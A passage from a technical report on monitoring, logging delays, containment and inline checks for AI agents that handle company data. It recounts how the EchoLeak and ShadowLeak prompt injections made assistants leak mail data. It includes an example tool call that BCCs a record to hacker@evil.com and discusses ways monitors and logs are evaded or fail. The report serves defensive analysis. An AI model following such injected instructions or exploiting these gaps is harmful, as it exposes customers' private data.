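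These records also help a team match actions in the vendor's logs to entries in other logs. Anthropic's events can include the user's ID, email address, network address and browser or app. Anthropic's *Compliance API* includes a sample event with all four, along with the time the user created a chat. A team could compare the network address with its own network logs to check whether the user was in the office. But that address would not help the team find the agent's reads in the customer database if the agent made them from Anthropic's servers.

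### Agents missing from the exports

Whether an agent appears in an export depends on the subscription, the product and the login. According to OpenAI's *Compliance API documentation*, the service is available only to ChatGPT Enterprise and Edu workspaces. Even in those workspaces, OpenAI says the export does not yet cover Atlas, its web browser with a built-in agent. It also warns that a company's data retention and deletion rules may not apply to the agent's activity in the browser.

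Whether the export includes a Claude Code session depends on how the employee signs in. If an employee signs in on a laptop with a Claude Enterprise account, Anthropic captures the session as requests reach its servers. If the employee uses an API key from Anthropic's developer console, or reaches Claude through Amazon's, Google's or Microsoft's cloud, the export contains no transcript. It also contains no prompts or responses from agents that a company builds with an Anthropic API key.

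This gap is manageable when the company runs the loop itself, because it can record the prompts and tool calls in its own software. Claude Code sessions that run in the cloud are harder to monitor, because they don't run on a company laptop and Anthropic excludes them from the transcripts. The event feed can still record that someone created a session. Its list of event types also refers to an hourly export of Claude Code's network activity, which might show where some sessions sent data.

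Like records from hooks, transcripts of sessions on a laptop do not show what a script did on the machine.

Some records exist only if the customer turns on logging. Microsoft includes its own Copilots and Copilot Studio agents in its standard audit service, but charges extra for records of other companies' AI applications and keeps those for 180 days. OpenAI says an owner has to turn on audit logging for its developer platform, which is separate from ChatGPT. Anthropic starts recording events when a customer first enables the Compliance API and does not add earlier activity, with a narrow exception for records of its own staff's access.

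### EchoLeak and ShadowLeak

In 2025, security researchers demonstrated two similar attacks that show how much it matters where the data leaves. In both, the attacker sent the victim an email containing hidden instructions for an AI assistant. The victim did not have to click anything. The assistant read the instructions while doing ordinary work, collected private data and put it in a web address.

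Researchers at Aim Labs reported EchoLeak, a vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot, to Microsoft in January 2025, and Microsoft completed a patch in May, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*. The program displaying Copilot's answer to the user sent the data out when it loaded an image. The request for the image contained the data and passed through a Microsoft Teams address that companies commonly trusted.

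ShadowLeak was a flaw in Deep Research, ChatGPT's agent for long research tasks, that affected users who had connected the agent to an email account. OpenAI's servers made the request to the attacker's site, so the data did not pass through the user's machine on the way. The security company Radware found the flaw and reported it on June 18, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in early August, according to SecurityWeek's *ChatGPT Targeted in Server-Side Data Theft Attack*. Radware tested the attack on Gmail but said Deep Research could also reach services such as Google Drive, Outlook and GitHub.

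The table compares what each observer could have recorded, assuming that the employee used a managed laptop on the company's network.

| Observer | EchoLeak | ShadowLeak |
|---|---|---|
| Software on the laptop | The program's connection to a Microsoft address | The employee's connection to ChatGPT |
| Proxy without decryption | A Microsoft host name | A ChatGPT host name |
| Proxy with TLS inspection | The full web address, including the data | The employee's question and ChatGPT's answer |
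| Application that held the data | Copilot's reads | ChatGPT's reads, if the application logs them |
| AI vendor | The reads and the answer containing the image address | The reads and the request to the attacker's site |

A company could have found an EchoLeak theft in its own records only if it had decrypted and kept its traffic to Microsoft, and many companies exempt such trusted services from inspection. Microsoft's audit record might not have helped much either. *EchoLeak*, a case study by Reddy and Gujral, reports that the attack evaded the classifier Microsoft used to detect prompt injection. If the audit field for prompt injection depends on the same classifier, it would have shown nothing wrong.

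With ShadowLeak, the company would have had to rely on OpenAI for any record of the request that carried the data away. Radware's *ShadowLeak* (2025) calls the leak "nearly impossible to detect" for the affected organization. Radware sells security products, including one for AI agents, so it benefits from making the danger seem large. But its main technical point is correct, because a request from OpenAI's servers to another website would not normally cross a customer's network.

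Radware exaggerates when it calls the organization "blind to the event". The attacker's email would still have been in the mailbox unless someone deleted it, and an investigator who already suspected an attack might have found the hidden instructions in it. The mail service could also have logged ChatGPT's reads, but these alone would have raised little suspicion, because the employee had asked ChatGPT to go through the mailbox.

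The same difference affects whether customers can check a vendor's assurances. Windows Central's *Microsoft Copilot's own default configuration exposed users* reports Microsoft's statement that attackers had not used EchoLeak to access customers' data. A customer with decrypted proxy logs could have searched them for suspicious image requests. For ShadowLeak, a customer seeking the same assurance would have had to ask OpenAI to search its records.

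### When a read is missing from the log

Application logs are useful only if the application records its reads. On July 4, 2025, Zack Korman of Pistachio was testing a product that relied on Copilot's audit log when he noticed by accident that Copilot sometimes summarized a file without the log showing that it had accessed the file. This suggests that the problem also occurred in ordinary use. He then found that a user could cause it deliberately. Pistachio says that Michael Bargury of the security company Zenity had reported the same problem a year earlier.

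The gap may have been narrower than Pistachio's description of an "empty" log implies. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* (2025) describes it as information missing from the audit events for Copilot's use of SharePoint files. If so, the log could contain an entry for the conversation without any reference to the file. Either way, an investigator who searched the log for a confidential document's name would not find who had read it through Copilot.

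Microsoft rated the flaw "important", one level below "critical", and told Korman that a full fix would arrive on August 17, 2025. It did not assign a CVE number, the public identifier companies use to track vulnerabilities, on the grounds that customers did not need to install anything. According to Pistachio, Microsoft also said it had no plans to inform customers. But the fix could not show customers which past entries were incomplete, so they still had reason to be told about the flaw after it was repaired.

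Office 365 for IT Pros confirmed on August 22 that Microsoft had fixed the records, and Microsoft's documentation now describes the list of accessed items as covering everything Copilot opened to answer a request. The documentation describes how the log should work, and customers trusted the log for that same reason before the fix. A company can test the log by having an employee ask Copilot about 50 known files, in different ways and from different applications, and checking whether all 50 appear. For events before August 18, 2025, a missing entry is weak evidence that nobody used Copilot to read a file.

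Vendors also leave some reads out of their logs on purpose. Anthropic used to log each time someone read the content of a project in Claude Design, its design tool, but it has retired that event type and no longer records those reads. A team that built an alert on the retired event would stop receiving warnings and might assume nothing was wrong. Anthropic also notes that some files users add to a Claude Code session produce no event.

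A customer can lose further entries while copying them, and Anthropic's lists include no total count or checksum (a value calculated from the data) that would reveal missing records. Entries can also arrive late, so a team that retrieves events one hour at a time and never rechecks earlier hours will miss any added to an hour it has already retrieved. Anthropic therefore recommends overlapping the periods or checking older ones again.

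### What settings and contracts can change

When an agent runs entirely in a vendor's cloud, the customer can get some information only if the vendor records and shares it. This includes the text that led the model to make a tool call, the inputs to the vendor's built-in tools, the web addresses the vendor's servers contacted, and whether the vendor's staff looked at the data. Logs from the applications that hold the data can show only the agent's requests to those applications.

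The customer can get better records by taking a few steps, most of which have to be in place before an incident. It can turn on the vendor's export and require employees to use company accounts that the export covers. For Claude Code and Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, it can also have telemetry sent to its own server while the agent works. If a cloud agent can reach the customer's internal systems only through the customer's own MCP gateway, the gateway keeps an independent record of the agent's calls to those systems. In a case like ShadowLeak, the gateway would have recorded ChatGPT's reads if the mailbox was behind it, but not the request to the attacker's site, because OpenAI's own browsing tool made that request.

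Anthropic keeps its event feed for six years but keeps the text of a chat only as long as the customer's policy allows. An employee can delete it sooner, after which the export still lists the chat but can't return its text. A company that needs the text for investigations has to copy it to its own archive as it arrives, which creates another store of sensitive data to protect.

Privacy settings can remove the evidence. Under zero data retention, the vendor does not keep prompts and responses after processing them, and Anthropic's export contains no transcripts of the affected sessions on users' machines. Customers with its settings for US health data get such transcripts only for Cowork and Claude Code, and only for 30 days. These settings reduce what a thief could steal from the vendor, but the company then has to record sessions itself or accept that it may never learn what an agent sent.

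Customers can close some gaps only by agreement with the vendor. A contract could require the vendor to log every outside address its agents contact, to search that log when the customer suspects a theft, and to disclose its staff's access to the customer's data. Anthropic already offers a record of staff access to customers who enroll in its Access Transparency program. A contract could also require the vendor to notify the customer when it discovers that its logs were incomplete or when it stops recording a type of event. Without such a clause, the vendor decides whether to tell customers about a gap, as Microsoft did with Copilot. Large customers are more likely to get these terms than small ones, which usually have to accept the vendor's standard contract.

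## Whether an observation comes in time to stop a loss

A complete and accurate log can still arrive too late to help John Doe. If the entry for the hidden BCC appears an hour after the agent sends the email, the security team can learn exactly what happened, but the attacker has had the account details for an hour. To prevent the loss, the team has to notice the problem, decide what to do and act while the company still controls the data.

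### Disclosure

In the example, the disclosure happens when the attacker's mail server accepts the copy, even if the attacker doesn't read it for weeks, because from then on the company cannot reliably recover the data.

The word "reliably" leaves room for judgment. If the agent mistakenly sends John Doe's record to the company's law firm, the company can usually believe a partner who confirms deleting the message, because the firm has a duty of confidentiality. The company would have no reason to trust the same confirmation from a stranger.

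The intended email to John Doe is also a disclosure, since the company can't get it back either. This section is mostly about whether the company can undo an action, which is a separate question from whether the action should have happened.

Passwords and keys are a partial exception because a company can cancel them after they leak, which it can't do with a medical diagnosis or a home address. When the malicious skill that Datadog's researchers studied sent out a GitHub token, the owner couldn't get the token back but could make the thief's copy useless by canceling it.

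### Three timings

An inline check holds an action until software or a person allows or blocks it. A Claude Code hook that reads the email tool's inputs before the tool runs can do this. An alert during the run comes after an action but while the agent is still working. A record after the event is a log or trace that people read only once the activity is over.

Whether a log entry is an alert or a record depends on when somebody reads it. The entry for step 1 is an alert if it reaches the team while the agent is still writing the email, but a record if an analyst opens it the next morning.

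"Real time" in product descriptions can refer to either of the first two timings. Google, for example, describes logs delayed by a couple of minutes as "near real time", but an agent can finish the whole John Doe task in less time than that.

### The timing condition

A team can prevent a disclosure only if:

*time to observe + time to decide + time to stop < time left before disclosure*

Timing starts at the event that gives the warning. The time to observe is how long the warning takes to reach the person or program that will judge it. The time to stop runs from the decision to stop the agent until it can no longer send the data, which may be well after someone presses a button.

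Suppose the agent opens John Doe's record at 10:14:00 and is due to send the email at 10:14:20. A detector finds the hidden instruction in the notes field and raises an alert 5 seconds after the read. If software then applies a rule in 1 second and takes another 10 to end the session, the session ends at 10:14:16, before the email goes out. If an analyst has to review the alert first and takes two minutes, the attacker gets the data.

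When the disclosure itself is the only warning, an alert comes too late to prevent the loss. This is true of the BCC, if nobody noticed anything odd about the read, and of a web address with a customer's phone number at the end. Preventing such a loss requires either an inline check or an earlier sign of trouble. Earlier events leave more time to act but usually provide less evidence of a problem, because agents read customer records all day for good reasons.

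An inline check holds an action, such as sending an email, until it decides whether to allow it. A slow check therefore delays work but doesn't let data out, provided it fails closed, meaning it blocks the action if it gets no answer. If it fails open after waiting 10 seconds, the answer must arrive within those 10 seconds to stop the loss. The check also has to recognize the bad action, which depends on its accuracy rather than its speed.

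Agents often send data in many portions, so an alert can come too late for some portions but in time for others. An alert that comes after the first hundred records have been sent may still allow the company to stop the next thousand, limiting the loss.

### Hard cases

Suppose an agent saves John Doe's record to a shared folder where it doesn't belong. If only employees can open the folder, no disclosure has happened yet, and the company can delete the file. Even if someone reads the log of the agent's actions only the next morning, that may be early enough to prevent a disclosure.

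Nobody knows how long the team has to delete the file. The deadline could be when a contractor with access to the folder downloads the file, or when the folder synchronizes with a partner's system. Deleting the file only prevents later reads, so the team also has to check the folder's log for earlier downloads. If the application doesn't log reads, the team can't tell whether it acted in time.

Some mail systems can hold outgoing messages for a set time. With a ten-minute hold, the team can still cancel the BCC'd email after the agent has finished its work. If an alert takes one minute to arrive, an analyst takes five to decide, and canceling the message takes one, the team has three minutes to spare.

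A delayed outbox can stop a loss only if the warning comes from a source that records the email before it leaves, such as the agent's own software. A mail log that adds an entry only on delivery would not help. The outbox sends the email unless someone objects, so a ten-minute hold offers little protection at night if nobody is on duty. The hold also doesn't apply if the agent sends the message through an outside service, as it would with the fake Postmark package.

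If a vendor runs the model, a record the agent opens normally reaches the vendor within moments.

Whether this is a disclosure depends on the provider's terms. If the provider keeps no prompts, the company has nothing to recover. A provider that must delete prompts on request is in much the same position as the law firm. But an alert about the read would come too late if an employee runs the agent through a personal account, where the company has no comparable assurance, or if the company has promised a client to keep the file in-house. In either case, the team would need an inline check before the read or an AI gateway that holds the request before it reaches the model.

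### How long logs take to arrive

Application logs are often the only record of what an agent read in a company's cloud services, so delays in these logs limit what a team can do with them. Microsoft (*Search the audit log*), Google (*Data retention and lag times*), AWS (*Working with CloudTrail log files*) and Salesforce (*Query or View Hourly Event Log Files*) publish figures for these delays. Salesforce also has a faster service, but the source used here is a security vendor's blog post, Imprivata's *Real-Time Event Monitoring* (2019), which gives no figure for the delay.

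| Log | Delay before an entry is available |
|---|---|
| Microsoft Purview audit: Exchange, SharePoint, OneDrive, Teams | Typically 60 to 90 minutes |
| Microsoft Purview audit: other services | May be longer |
| Google Workspace: Drive, Gmail and Gemini | A couple of minutes |
| Google Workspace: tokens | A couple of hours |
| Google Workspace: OAuth | Up to a few hours |
| AWS CloudTrail | About 5 minutes on average |
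| Salesforce real-time events | "Near real time" |
| Salesforce hourly event log files | Three to six hours, sometimes longer |

Microsoft and AWS say they don't guarantee these times, and Google warns that some events may arrive later than stated or, in rare cases, never. Microsoft used to publish a table of delays for each service, ranging from 30 minutes to 24 hours, but withdrew it in April 2022, according to michev.info's *Microsoft 365/Azure AD audit logs and reports latency data*.

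Practical 365, a site for Microsoft administrators, recommends using Microsoft's audit log to reconstruct past events rather than monitor current ones. This is right for agents, because an agent that empties a SharePoint folder in ten minutes will usually have finished almost an hour before the first entry appears. Microsoft's examples of core services do not include Copilot, so even the 60-to-90-minute delay may not apply to Copilot's records.

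Google's Drive log shows file reads much sooner than its token log shows permission grants. If an employee connects an unapproved agent to a work account, the team may see the agent's reads an hour or more before it sees the grant. If the team relies on the token log to find undeclared agents, a new agent therefore has access to the data for a couple of hours before the team can detect it.

Salesforce offers the widest choice. Late events missing from an hourly file go into a new file for the same hour. According to Salesforce's *Differences Between Hourly and 24-Hour Event Logs*, a company can instead get one file for every 24 hours of activity. An event early in the day then waits at least until the day is over. The real-time service streams events as they happen and can apply rules to some types of event. sfitdelivery's *SF Event Monitoring*, a set of notes for Salesforce staff, mentions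 rules that block suspicious actions automatically, which would make them inline checks. According to *Salesforce Real-Time Events*, part of the documentation for the log analysis product Panther, customers must pay for an add-on subscription to use the service and can stream at most 30 types of event to Panther.

### A closer look at CloudTrail

CloudTrail, which logs activity in Amazon's cloud, is the only one of the four for which we have an outsider's measurements. *How fast is CloudTrail today?* (Cox, 2023) compares the time of each event with the time its log file arrived, using a week of data from the accounts of Cox's company, Tracebit. The average delay was about two and a half minutes, and 99% of events arrived within just over five minutes. Fewer than 1 in 3,000 took longer than ten minutes, but the slowest took over 16 hours, and Cox found nothing unusual about the events that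 took several hours.

Cox suggests that the pattern arises because CloudTrail collects events in a buffer before writing them to a file. The first event in an account and region opens the buffer and starts a five-minute timer. Later events join the buffer, and CloudTrail writes them all to one file when the timer runs out. The first event therefore waits the full five minutes, while one that arrives just before the deadline waits a few seconds. Cox tested this on 1,000 events from each account and region, and the delays matched. Nearly every event took five minutes in a region with little activity, so he points out that an intruder could stay unnoticed for longer by working in a region the company rarely uses.

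These numbers come from one company in 2023, and Tracebit sells a detection product that depends on CloudTrail. But they agree with AWS's own figure and, if anything, suggest that CloudTrail is faster than AWS says.

A shorter logging delay doesn't help if the log omits the event. AWS's *CloudTrail concepts* explains that CloudTrail by default logs management events, such as changes to an account's settings, but not data events, which include reads of stored files. Unless someone has turned on logging for data events, an agent can download every customer file without CloudTrail recording the reads.

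Delivery is also only part of the delay between an event and its alert. A Panther customer measured this delay at about 15 minutes and asked whether it could be shortened. Panther replied that CloudTrail takes roughly five minutes to deliver, which Panther could not reduce. The other ten minutes presumably went to collecting the file, reading it and running the detection rules.

### Thirty thousand records in five minutes

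To see what a five-minute delay costs, assume the following:

- The agent reads 200 customer records with each call.
- It makes one call every two seconds.
- It sends each batch to an outside party immediately.
- The first log entry arrives five minutes after the first call.

In five minutes, the agent can make 150 calls. At 200 records per call, it has disclosed 30,000 records by the time the first entry arrives. If CloudTrail works as Cox thinks, the first file will list nearly all of these calls at once, so the team will see no sign of the theft until it is already large.

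The agent keeps working while the team decides what to do. At 100 records a second, it can disclose another 60,000 records in the ten minutes an analyst needs to confirm the theft, and 6,000 more for each minute spent finding the right button. If log entries arrive after 60 minutes, the low end of Microsoft's range, the agent could disclose 360,000 records before the first entry appears. If they arrive after three hours, the low end for Salesforce's hourly files, it could disclose 1,080,000.

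Most customer tables are smaller than that, so the theft often ends before the log arrives. At the same speed, a table of 40,000 customers takes 400 seconds to copy. With a five-minute delay, 100 seconds remain to protect the last 10,000 records. If the alert comes 15 minutes after the event, the whole table has already been copied.

The third assumption matters most. If the agent collects all 40,000 records before sending any, and then sends them all at once, the team that gets its first entry after five minutes still has 100 seconds to prevent the entire loss. An automatic response could act in that time, but an analyst probably could not. But if one call can return the whole table, there is no series of calls to interrupt.

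Slower theft gives the team more time to limit the loss. An agent that sends out one record a minute has disclosed about five when the first log entry arrives. But slow theft also looks much more like normal work, so the team may need weeks instead of minutes to decide whether it is theft.

A company can limit the loss without observing anything by capping how much an agent may read. With a cap of 1,000 records an hour, the agent in the example reaches the limit after five calls, within ten seconds, so the company loses at most 1,000 records during a five-minute log delay. The cap has to be low enough to limit the loss but still allow ordinary work, which is easier for an agent that answers one customer at a time than for one that writes monthly reports.

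Agents can do other irreversible damage just as quickly. Clubic's *Qui a donné à l'IA l'accès aux données sensibles ?* describes an April 2026 incident at a company called PocketOS, in which a coding agent ran into a credential error, found an API key unrelated to its task, and used it to delete the production database and the backups in nine seconds. Every delay the table gives in minutes or hours is much longer than that.

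### Containment

Once a team decides to stop an agent, it has four main ways to do so. Each step here stops something that the one before it may leave running:

1. **Revoke the token.** The server that issued the token stops renewing it, and applications that check with that server reject further requests. The agent loses access to those services but keeps running, with everything it has already read still in its context.
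2. **End the session.** The team closes the agent's logged-in sessions and open connections in each application, and cancels the agent's run if a vendor hosts it. The agent then has to log in again, which fails if its credentials no longer work.
3. **Kill the process.** On a laptop or server, EDR can stop the program that runs the loop. It also has to stop the scripts and other programs the agent started, since these can continue after their parent has gone.
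4. **Isolate the machine.** EDR blocks all of the machine's network connections except its own. This also stops programs that the team has not found, including a script that the computer's scheduler starts an hour later.

Even isolation can't recall a message that has already reached the mail service. It also doesn't remove forwarding rules or public links that the agent created in cloud applications, and these can keep disclosing data after the agent has stopped. The team has to check each application for them.

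The order of these steps can vary. If the agent runs on one employee's laptop and is sending out 100 records a second, isolating the laptop first may be quickest, though it interrupts the employee. If a vendor runs the agent in its cloud, the company has no machine to isolate and can take only the first two steps. If ten agents share a service account, revoking its key to stop one agent also stops the other nine, so a team may hesitate. Giving each agent and session a separate identity therefore shortens the time to decide, because a mistaken stop does less harm.

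### Why an agent can continue without its credentials

Help Net Security's *AI agents keep access to company data after their work is done* reports that some organizations can revoke credentials at once but need more time to end the agent's session.

Many access tokens are self-contained. The issuing server signs the token and writes an expiry time into it, and the application checks only the signature and the time. The application therefore doesn't have to contact the issuing server for every request, but it also doesn't detect that a token has been revoked. A revoked token works until it expires, often about an hour after it was issued. At the speed in the example, an agent could get through 360,000 records in an hour.

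Other applications check a credential only at login. A database typically requires a password when a program opens a connection, then accepts queries until the connection closes. A website may give the browser a cookie after login, a piece of text that the browser sends with each later request. Changing the password does not close the open connection and may not invalidate the cookie.

The agent may also have another way to get access. In the PocketOS case, the agent used a key that nobody had given it for the task. And an agent that has already read the data can disclose it without access to the database. If the team revokes the database token after step 1 of the John Doe example, the agent can still send the email because the record is already in its context.

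The reverse problem, a credential that outlasts its session, is also common. In a survey by the identity security vendor Delinea, 42% of IT and security leaders said their organizations had no automatic way to remove an AI tool's access when a session ended. The leftover credential can enable a later theft, though it doesn't prolong one already in progress.

### What companies say about their own speed

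The same survey, Delinea (2026), is the largest source of figures on how quickly companies notice agents exceeding their scope. It covered 2,254 IT and security leaders and 2,250 other employees in eight countries, all at organizations that use AI and have at least 500 employees. Almost all the leaders (99.7%) said their organization had a formal policy on which data AI tools may access, but only about 51% of organizations checked access against the policy in real time. When an AI tool or agent most recently exceeded its scope, 19% noticed as it happened, while 55% took at least a day.

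That leaves at most about a quarter who noticed later the same day. Even they would have been too late to interrupt the theft of 40,000 records, which takes less than seven minutes.

Real-time checks may work more often than the gap between 51% and 19% suggests. When a check blocks an agent, there is no out-of-scope access to report, so the second figure may leave out the check's successes. But leaders can only report cases that somebody discovered, and counting the undiscovered ones would bring the share noticed at the time below 19%.

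Delinea has a commercial interest in these results. Two months before publishing them, Delinea (2026) launched a product that checks each of an agent's actions before it runs, and called it the only platform to do so. That claim is hard to reconcile with Claude Code's hooks and the similar checkpoint in Copilot Studio. The survey also recommends authorizing access at the moment of action, which is what the product does. This doesn't make the answers false, but it gave Delinea a reason to define the problem broadly when designing the survey.

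The 51% figure should not be compared with an earlier survey by the same company, because the questions were different. In March, Delinea (2026) reported that fewer than one in three organizations validated the activity of AI agents and other non-human accounts in real time, but the survey question behind that figure concerned whether companies could find all such accounts.

A second vendor's survey had similar results. Cequence Security's *New Cequence & EMA Research* (2026), conducted with the research firm Enterprise Management Associates, reports that 34% of organizations evaluate an agent's authorization when it attempts an action. About 32% can detect and contain an out-of-scope action automatically within minutes, and 55% need hours and manual steps. Roughly 4% first learned of trouble from a customer or partner. Cequence also sells protection for agents, and its announcement doesn't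 give the number of respondents.

The closest thing to an independent check is a survey by ISACA, a professional association for auditors and security staff that sells training and certificates in AI security but no monitoring software. ISACA (2026) asked more than 3,400 professionals how quickly they could halt an AI system because of a security incident. About 56% did not know, 32% believed they could do it within 60 minutes, and 7% said it would take longer. The results support the broader finding that few companies are ready to interrupt an agent mid-task. They can't confirm Delinea's figures on detection, because the question covered all AI systems, not just agents, and measured only the time to stop them.

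ISACA also asked how people oversee AI-generated actions, and the answers roughly match the three timings. Of the respondents, 36% said humans approve most actions before execution, 11% said humans intervene only when something alerts them, and 26% said humans review selected decisions or patterns afterwards. Another 20% did not know. The 36% seems high for agents that make dozens of tool calls per task, and may largely reflect simpler systems, such as an assistant whose drafts an employee reads before sending.

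Few respondents can base their estimates on practice. ISACA reports in the full poll results that only 12% have a documented and regularly tested process for shutting down or overriding AI systems. A company can get a better figure from a drill in which a test agent reads invented customer records at a steady rate. The team notes when the first alert arrives, when someone decides to act and when the agent's last call succeeds. The last time is the most likely to surprise the team, because the agent's calls can keep succeeding after someone has revoked its token.

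## Checks before an action runs

A revoked token can keep working for an hour, so it is often hard to stop an agent that has begun to leak data before it leaks more. An inline check avoids this problem because the action waits until the check finishes. But somebody has to decide what happens when the check returns no result, and employees will press to have it removed if it blocks too much harmless work.

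### The Copilot Studio check

Copilot Studio lets a company connect an outside security service that judges each tool call before it runs. The service can be Microsoft Defender, another vendor's product or something the company wrote itself. The BCC in the John Doe case comes from the example that Microsoft publishes for developers of such services, which works like this:

1. An employee asks the agent to send an email to the customer. The agent asks which one, and the employee names John Doe.
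2. The agent looks up John Doe's address with another tool.
3. The agent chooses the email tool and fills in its inputs, with the customer's address under "to" and hacker@evil.com under "bcc".
4. Copilot Studio holds the call and sends the details to the security service. They include the employee's latest message, the chat history, the result of the address lookup, the agent's reason for choosing the tool, a description of the tool and the proposed inputs.
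5. The service replies that Copilot Studio should block the call, with a reason code and an explanation that the BCC field contains a noncompliant address.
6. Copilot Studio does not run the tool. The agent stops and tells the employee that it blocked their message.

Microsoft leaves the service to work out that the address is noncompliant. A simple rule would block any recipient that the employee did not type and no earlier tool returned. That rule works in Microsoft's example, where the attacker's address appears only in the BCC field. It fails if the address came from a hidden instruction in the notes field of John Doe's record, because an earlier tool would then have returned it. To catch this case, the service would have to distinguish an address in the customer database's email field from one in the notes.

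The service may also not receive all the context it needs. Microsoft describes the chat history and tool outputs as "recent", so an instruction from early in a long conversation could be missing. The chat history, the tool outputs and the agent's reason for the action are all optional fields.

Some services ignore most of what they receive. CrowdStrike's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector* says the product analyzes only the tool's name and inputs, although Copilot Studio also sends it the prompt, history and earlier outputs. The product could block the BCC if a rule covered that address or domain, but it could not compare the address with the employee's request. Palo Alto Networks' *Configure SaaS Agent Security as an External Threat Detection System* describes a service that analyzes prompts for malicious intent. The employee's prompt is harmless here, so a service that analyzed only the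 prompt would find nothing wrong.

Copilot Studio runs the check only for agents whose model chooses the tools, not for older agents that follow a fixed script. According to Microsoft's *Protect your environment in real-time during agent runtime*, Defender still blocks suspicious calls if nobody has connected it to Microsoft 365, but no alert appears in the security team's portal.

### When no answer arrives

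The security service has 1,000 milliseconds to answer. By default the check fails open, so if the answer is late, Copilot Studio runs the tool.

Microsoft's documentation is inconsistent about whether a company can change how an agent handles a late answer. The instructions for developers say that the agent treats a late answer as "allow" and mention no alternative. The instructions for administrators describe a setting for errors and late answers that lets the company choose between allowing the agent to respond and blocking the query. But a note on the same page says that the tool will run if no answer arrives within one second, and makes no exception for companies that chose to block. *Defender for Cloud Apps Helps Protect Copilot Studio Agents* (Miller, 2025), an independent analyst's report, also describes only the fail-open behavior. CrowdStrike says that Copilot Studio applies whichever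 setting the company chose.

Most likely, the block setting does cover late answers and the note describes the default. A company that depends on this should test it by connecting a service that waits two seconds before answering, choosing the block setting and asking an agent to send an email.

It is also unclear whether the feature has left preview. The public preview began on September 4, 2025. A Microsoft notice reposted by the IT firm itelio set general availability for December 10, 2025, but Microsoft's release plan for April to September 2026 still listed it for June 2026. The instructions for administrators include a warning that preview features are not meant for production use.

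Failing open and failing closed both have drawbacks. Suppose a company's agents make a million tool calls a day and the service responds too late to one call in a thousand. If the check fails open, 1,000 calls a day run unchecked. If it fails closed, it blocks about 1,000 calls a day, nearly all of them harmless, and an outage at the security vendor stops every agent that uses tools. Copilot Studio keeps agents in containers called environments, and administrators can configure the check separately for each one. A company could therefore have the check fail closed for agents that email customers and fail open for an agent that only looks up opening hours.

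Protection can also lapse because of an administrative change. On July 1, 2026, Microsoft moved several agent security features to a new license called Agent 365. It warned customers with existing blocking rules in Agent 365 that those rules would stop blocking that day until someone redefined them on a new policy page. In the notice, Microsoft lists real-time protection for Copilot Studio among the features that customers lose without the license, but also says this protection is unchanged for customers who use it through Defender for Cloud Apps. To be sure the protection still works, an administrator would have to try a call that it should block.

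### Rules a monitor can enforce

Even a check that always finishes in time can enforce only certain kinds of rule. *Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) identifies which rules can be enforced by a monitor that follows a program step by step and stops it before a step that would break the rule. Such a monitor has a record of the steps so far, but no information about later steps or about what the program would have done in other circumstances.

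Schneider showed that any rule this kind of monitor can enforce meets three conditions:

- Each run of the program can be judged on its own. If Π is the set of all the program's possible runs and *P* is the rule, there must be a test *p* for single runs such that *P*(Π) is true exactly when *p*(σ) is true for every run σ in Π.
- Once a partial run has broken the rule, nothing the program does later can repair it.
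- Every run that breaks the rule does so after a finite number of steps.

Rules that meet all three are called safety properties, and they prohibit a particular bad thing from ever happening. One example is "The agent never emails anyone outside the approved list." "The agent eventually deletes its working copies" isn't a safety property because the agent could always delete them later, but adding a deadline, such as one hour, makes it one. Similarly, Schneider notes that a rule that nobody waits forever for a resource becomes a safety property once it has a maximum waiting time.

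A monitor that can only stop the agent can enforce a policy only if the policy is a safety property, but it can't enforce every safety property. For example, it can't enforce a rule that the agent delete a file by a deadline, because stopping the agent leaves the file in place. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, by Basin, Jugé and colleagues, refines Schneider's account by separating actions that a monitor can prevent, such as sending an email, from those it can only observe, such as the passing of an hour.

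One of Schneider's examples, a rule that a program may not send anything after it has read a file, is close to the problem with agents. The monitor needs only two states, "no file read" and "file read". It starts in the first, where it allows everything, and switches to the second as soon as the program reads a file. From then on it rejects every attempt to send. This would stop an agent that has read John Doe's record from leaking it, but also from emailing John Doe.

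Separate monitors can run together and enforce all of their rules. A company can therefore use one to check recipients, another to check for card numbers and a third to cap how many records an agent reads, without building a single system for all three.

### Monitors that change actions

Schneider's monitors can only stop a program. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker (2003), in *Edit Automata*, compared four kinds of monitor with different powers. In the John Doe example, they could do the following:

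| Kind of monitor | What it could do about the email |
|---|---|
| Truncation | End the agent's run before the email goes out |
| Suppression | Drop the email and let the agent go on to the support ticket |
| Insertion | Add an action of its own, such as saving a record of the attempt before ending the run |
| Edit | Remove the BCC and send the email to John Doe |

Copilot Studio's check can allow or block a tool call but can't change it. CrowdStrike customers can use rules that alter content in other systems, but if they apply such a rule to Copilot Studio, CrowdStrike reports the problem and allows the call. A rule meant to remove card numbers from outgoing emails would therefore let the emails go out unchanged. A Claude Code hook is closer to an edit monitor because it can rewrite a tool's inputs.

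Ligatti and colleagues require a good monitor to be sound, meaning that everything it lets through obeys the rule, and transparent, meaning that it doesn't change the effect of a run that already obeyed the rule. A monitor that blocks everything is sound but useless. Most practical disputes about inline checks concern transparency, such as when a check sometimes blocks legitimate emails.

An edit monitor can also hold an action and release it later, as a delayed outbox does. Ligatti and colleagues point out that any delay can change what a program does if the program needs the action's result to continue. Long holds are therefore practical for many sends but rarely for reads. The agent can open the support ticket while its email waits in the outbox, but it needs John Doe's record before it can write the email.

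### Why information flow is harder

A company usually wants to limit what an outsider can learn, and Schneider's monitors cannot enforce that kind of rule exactly. Suppose a supplier asks the agent whether John Doe pays his bills, and the agent replies, "We don't comment on customers." The supplier learns nothing if the agent gives that reply about everyone, but learns that John Doe has missed payments if the agent gives it only about customers who have missed payments and praises all the others.

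The email is identical in both cases. The cases differ in the reply the agent would have given about another customer, which a monitor that follows one run cannot observe. Rules about information flow therefore do not meet the condition that each run can be judged on its own.

Blocking can itself leak information. If a check blocks replies only about customers in debt, a supplier who asks about a customer and gets no reply can infer that the customer is in debt. Blocking can't violate a safety property in this way, because removing some of a program's possible runs never breaks one.

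Monitors meant to prevent information flow actually enforce a stricter rule, such as forbidding the agent to email outsiders at all after it opens a customer's payment history. This rule also blocks many harmless emails. Schneider notes that the extreme case is a rule that forbids every run, which is perfectly secure but lets the agent do no work.

### Labels that follow the data

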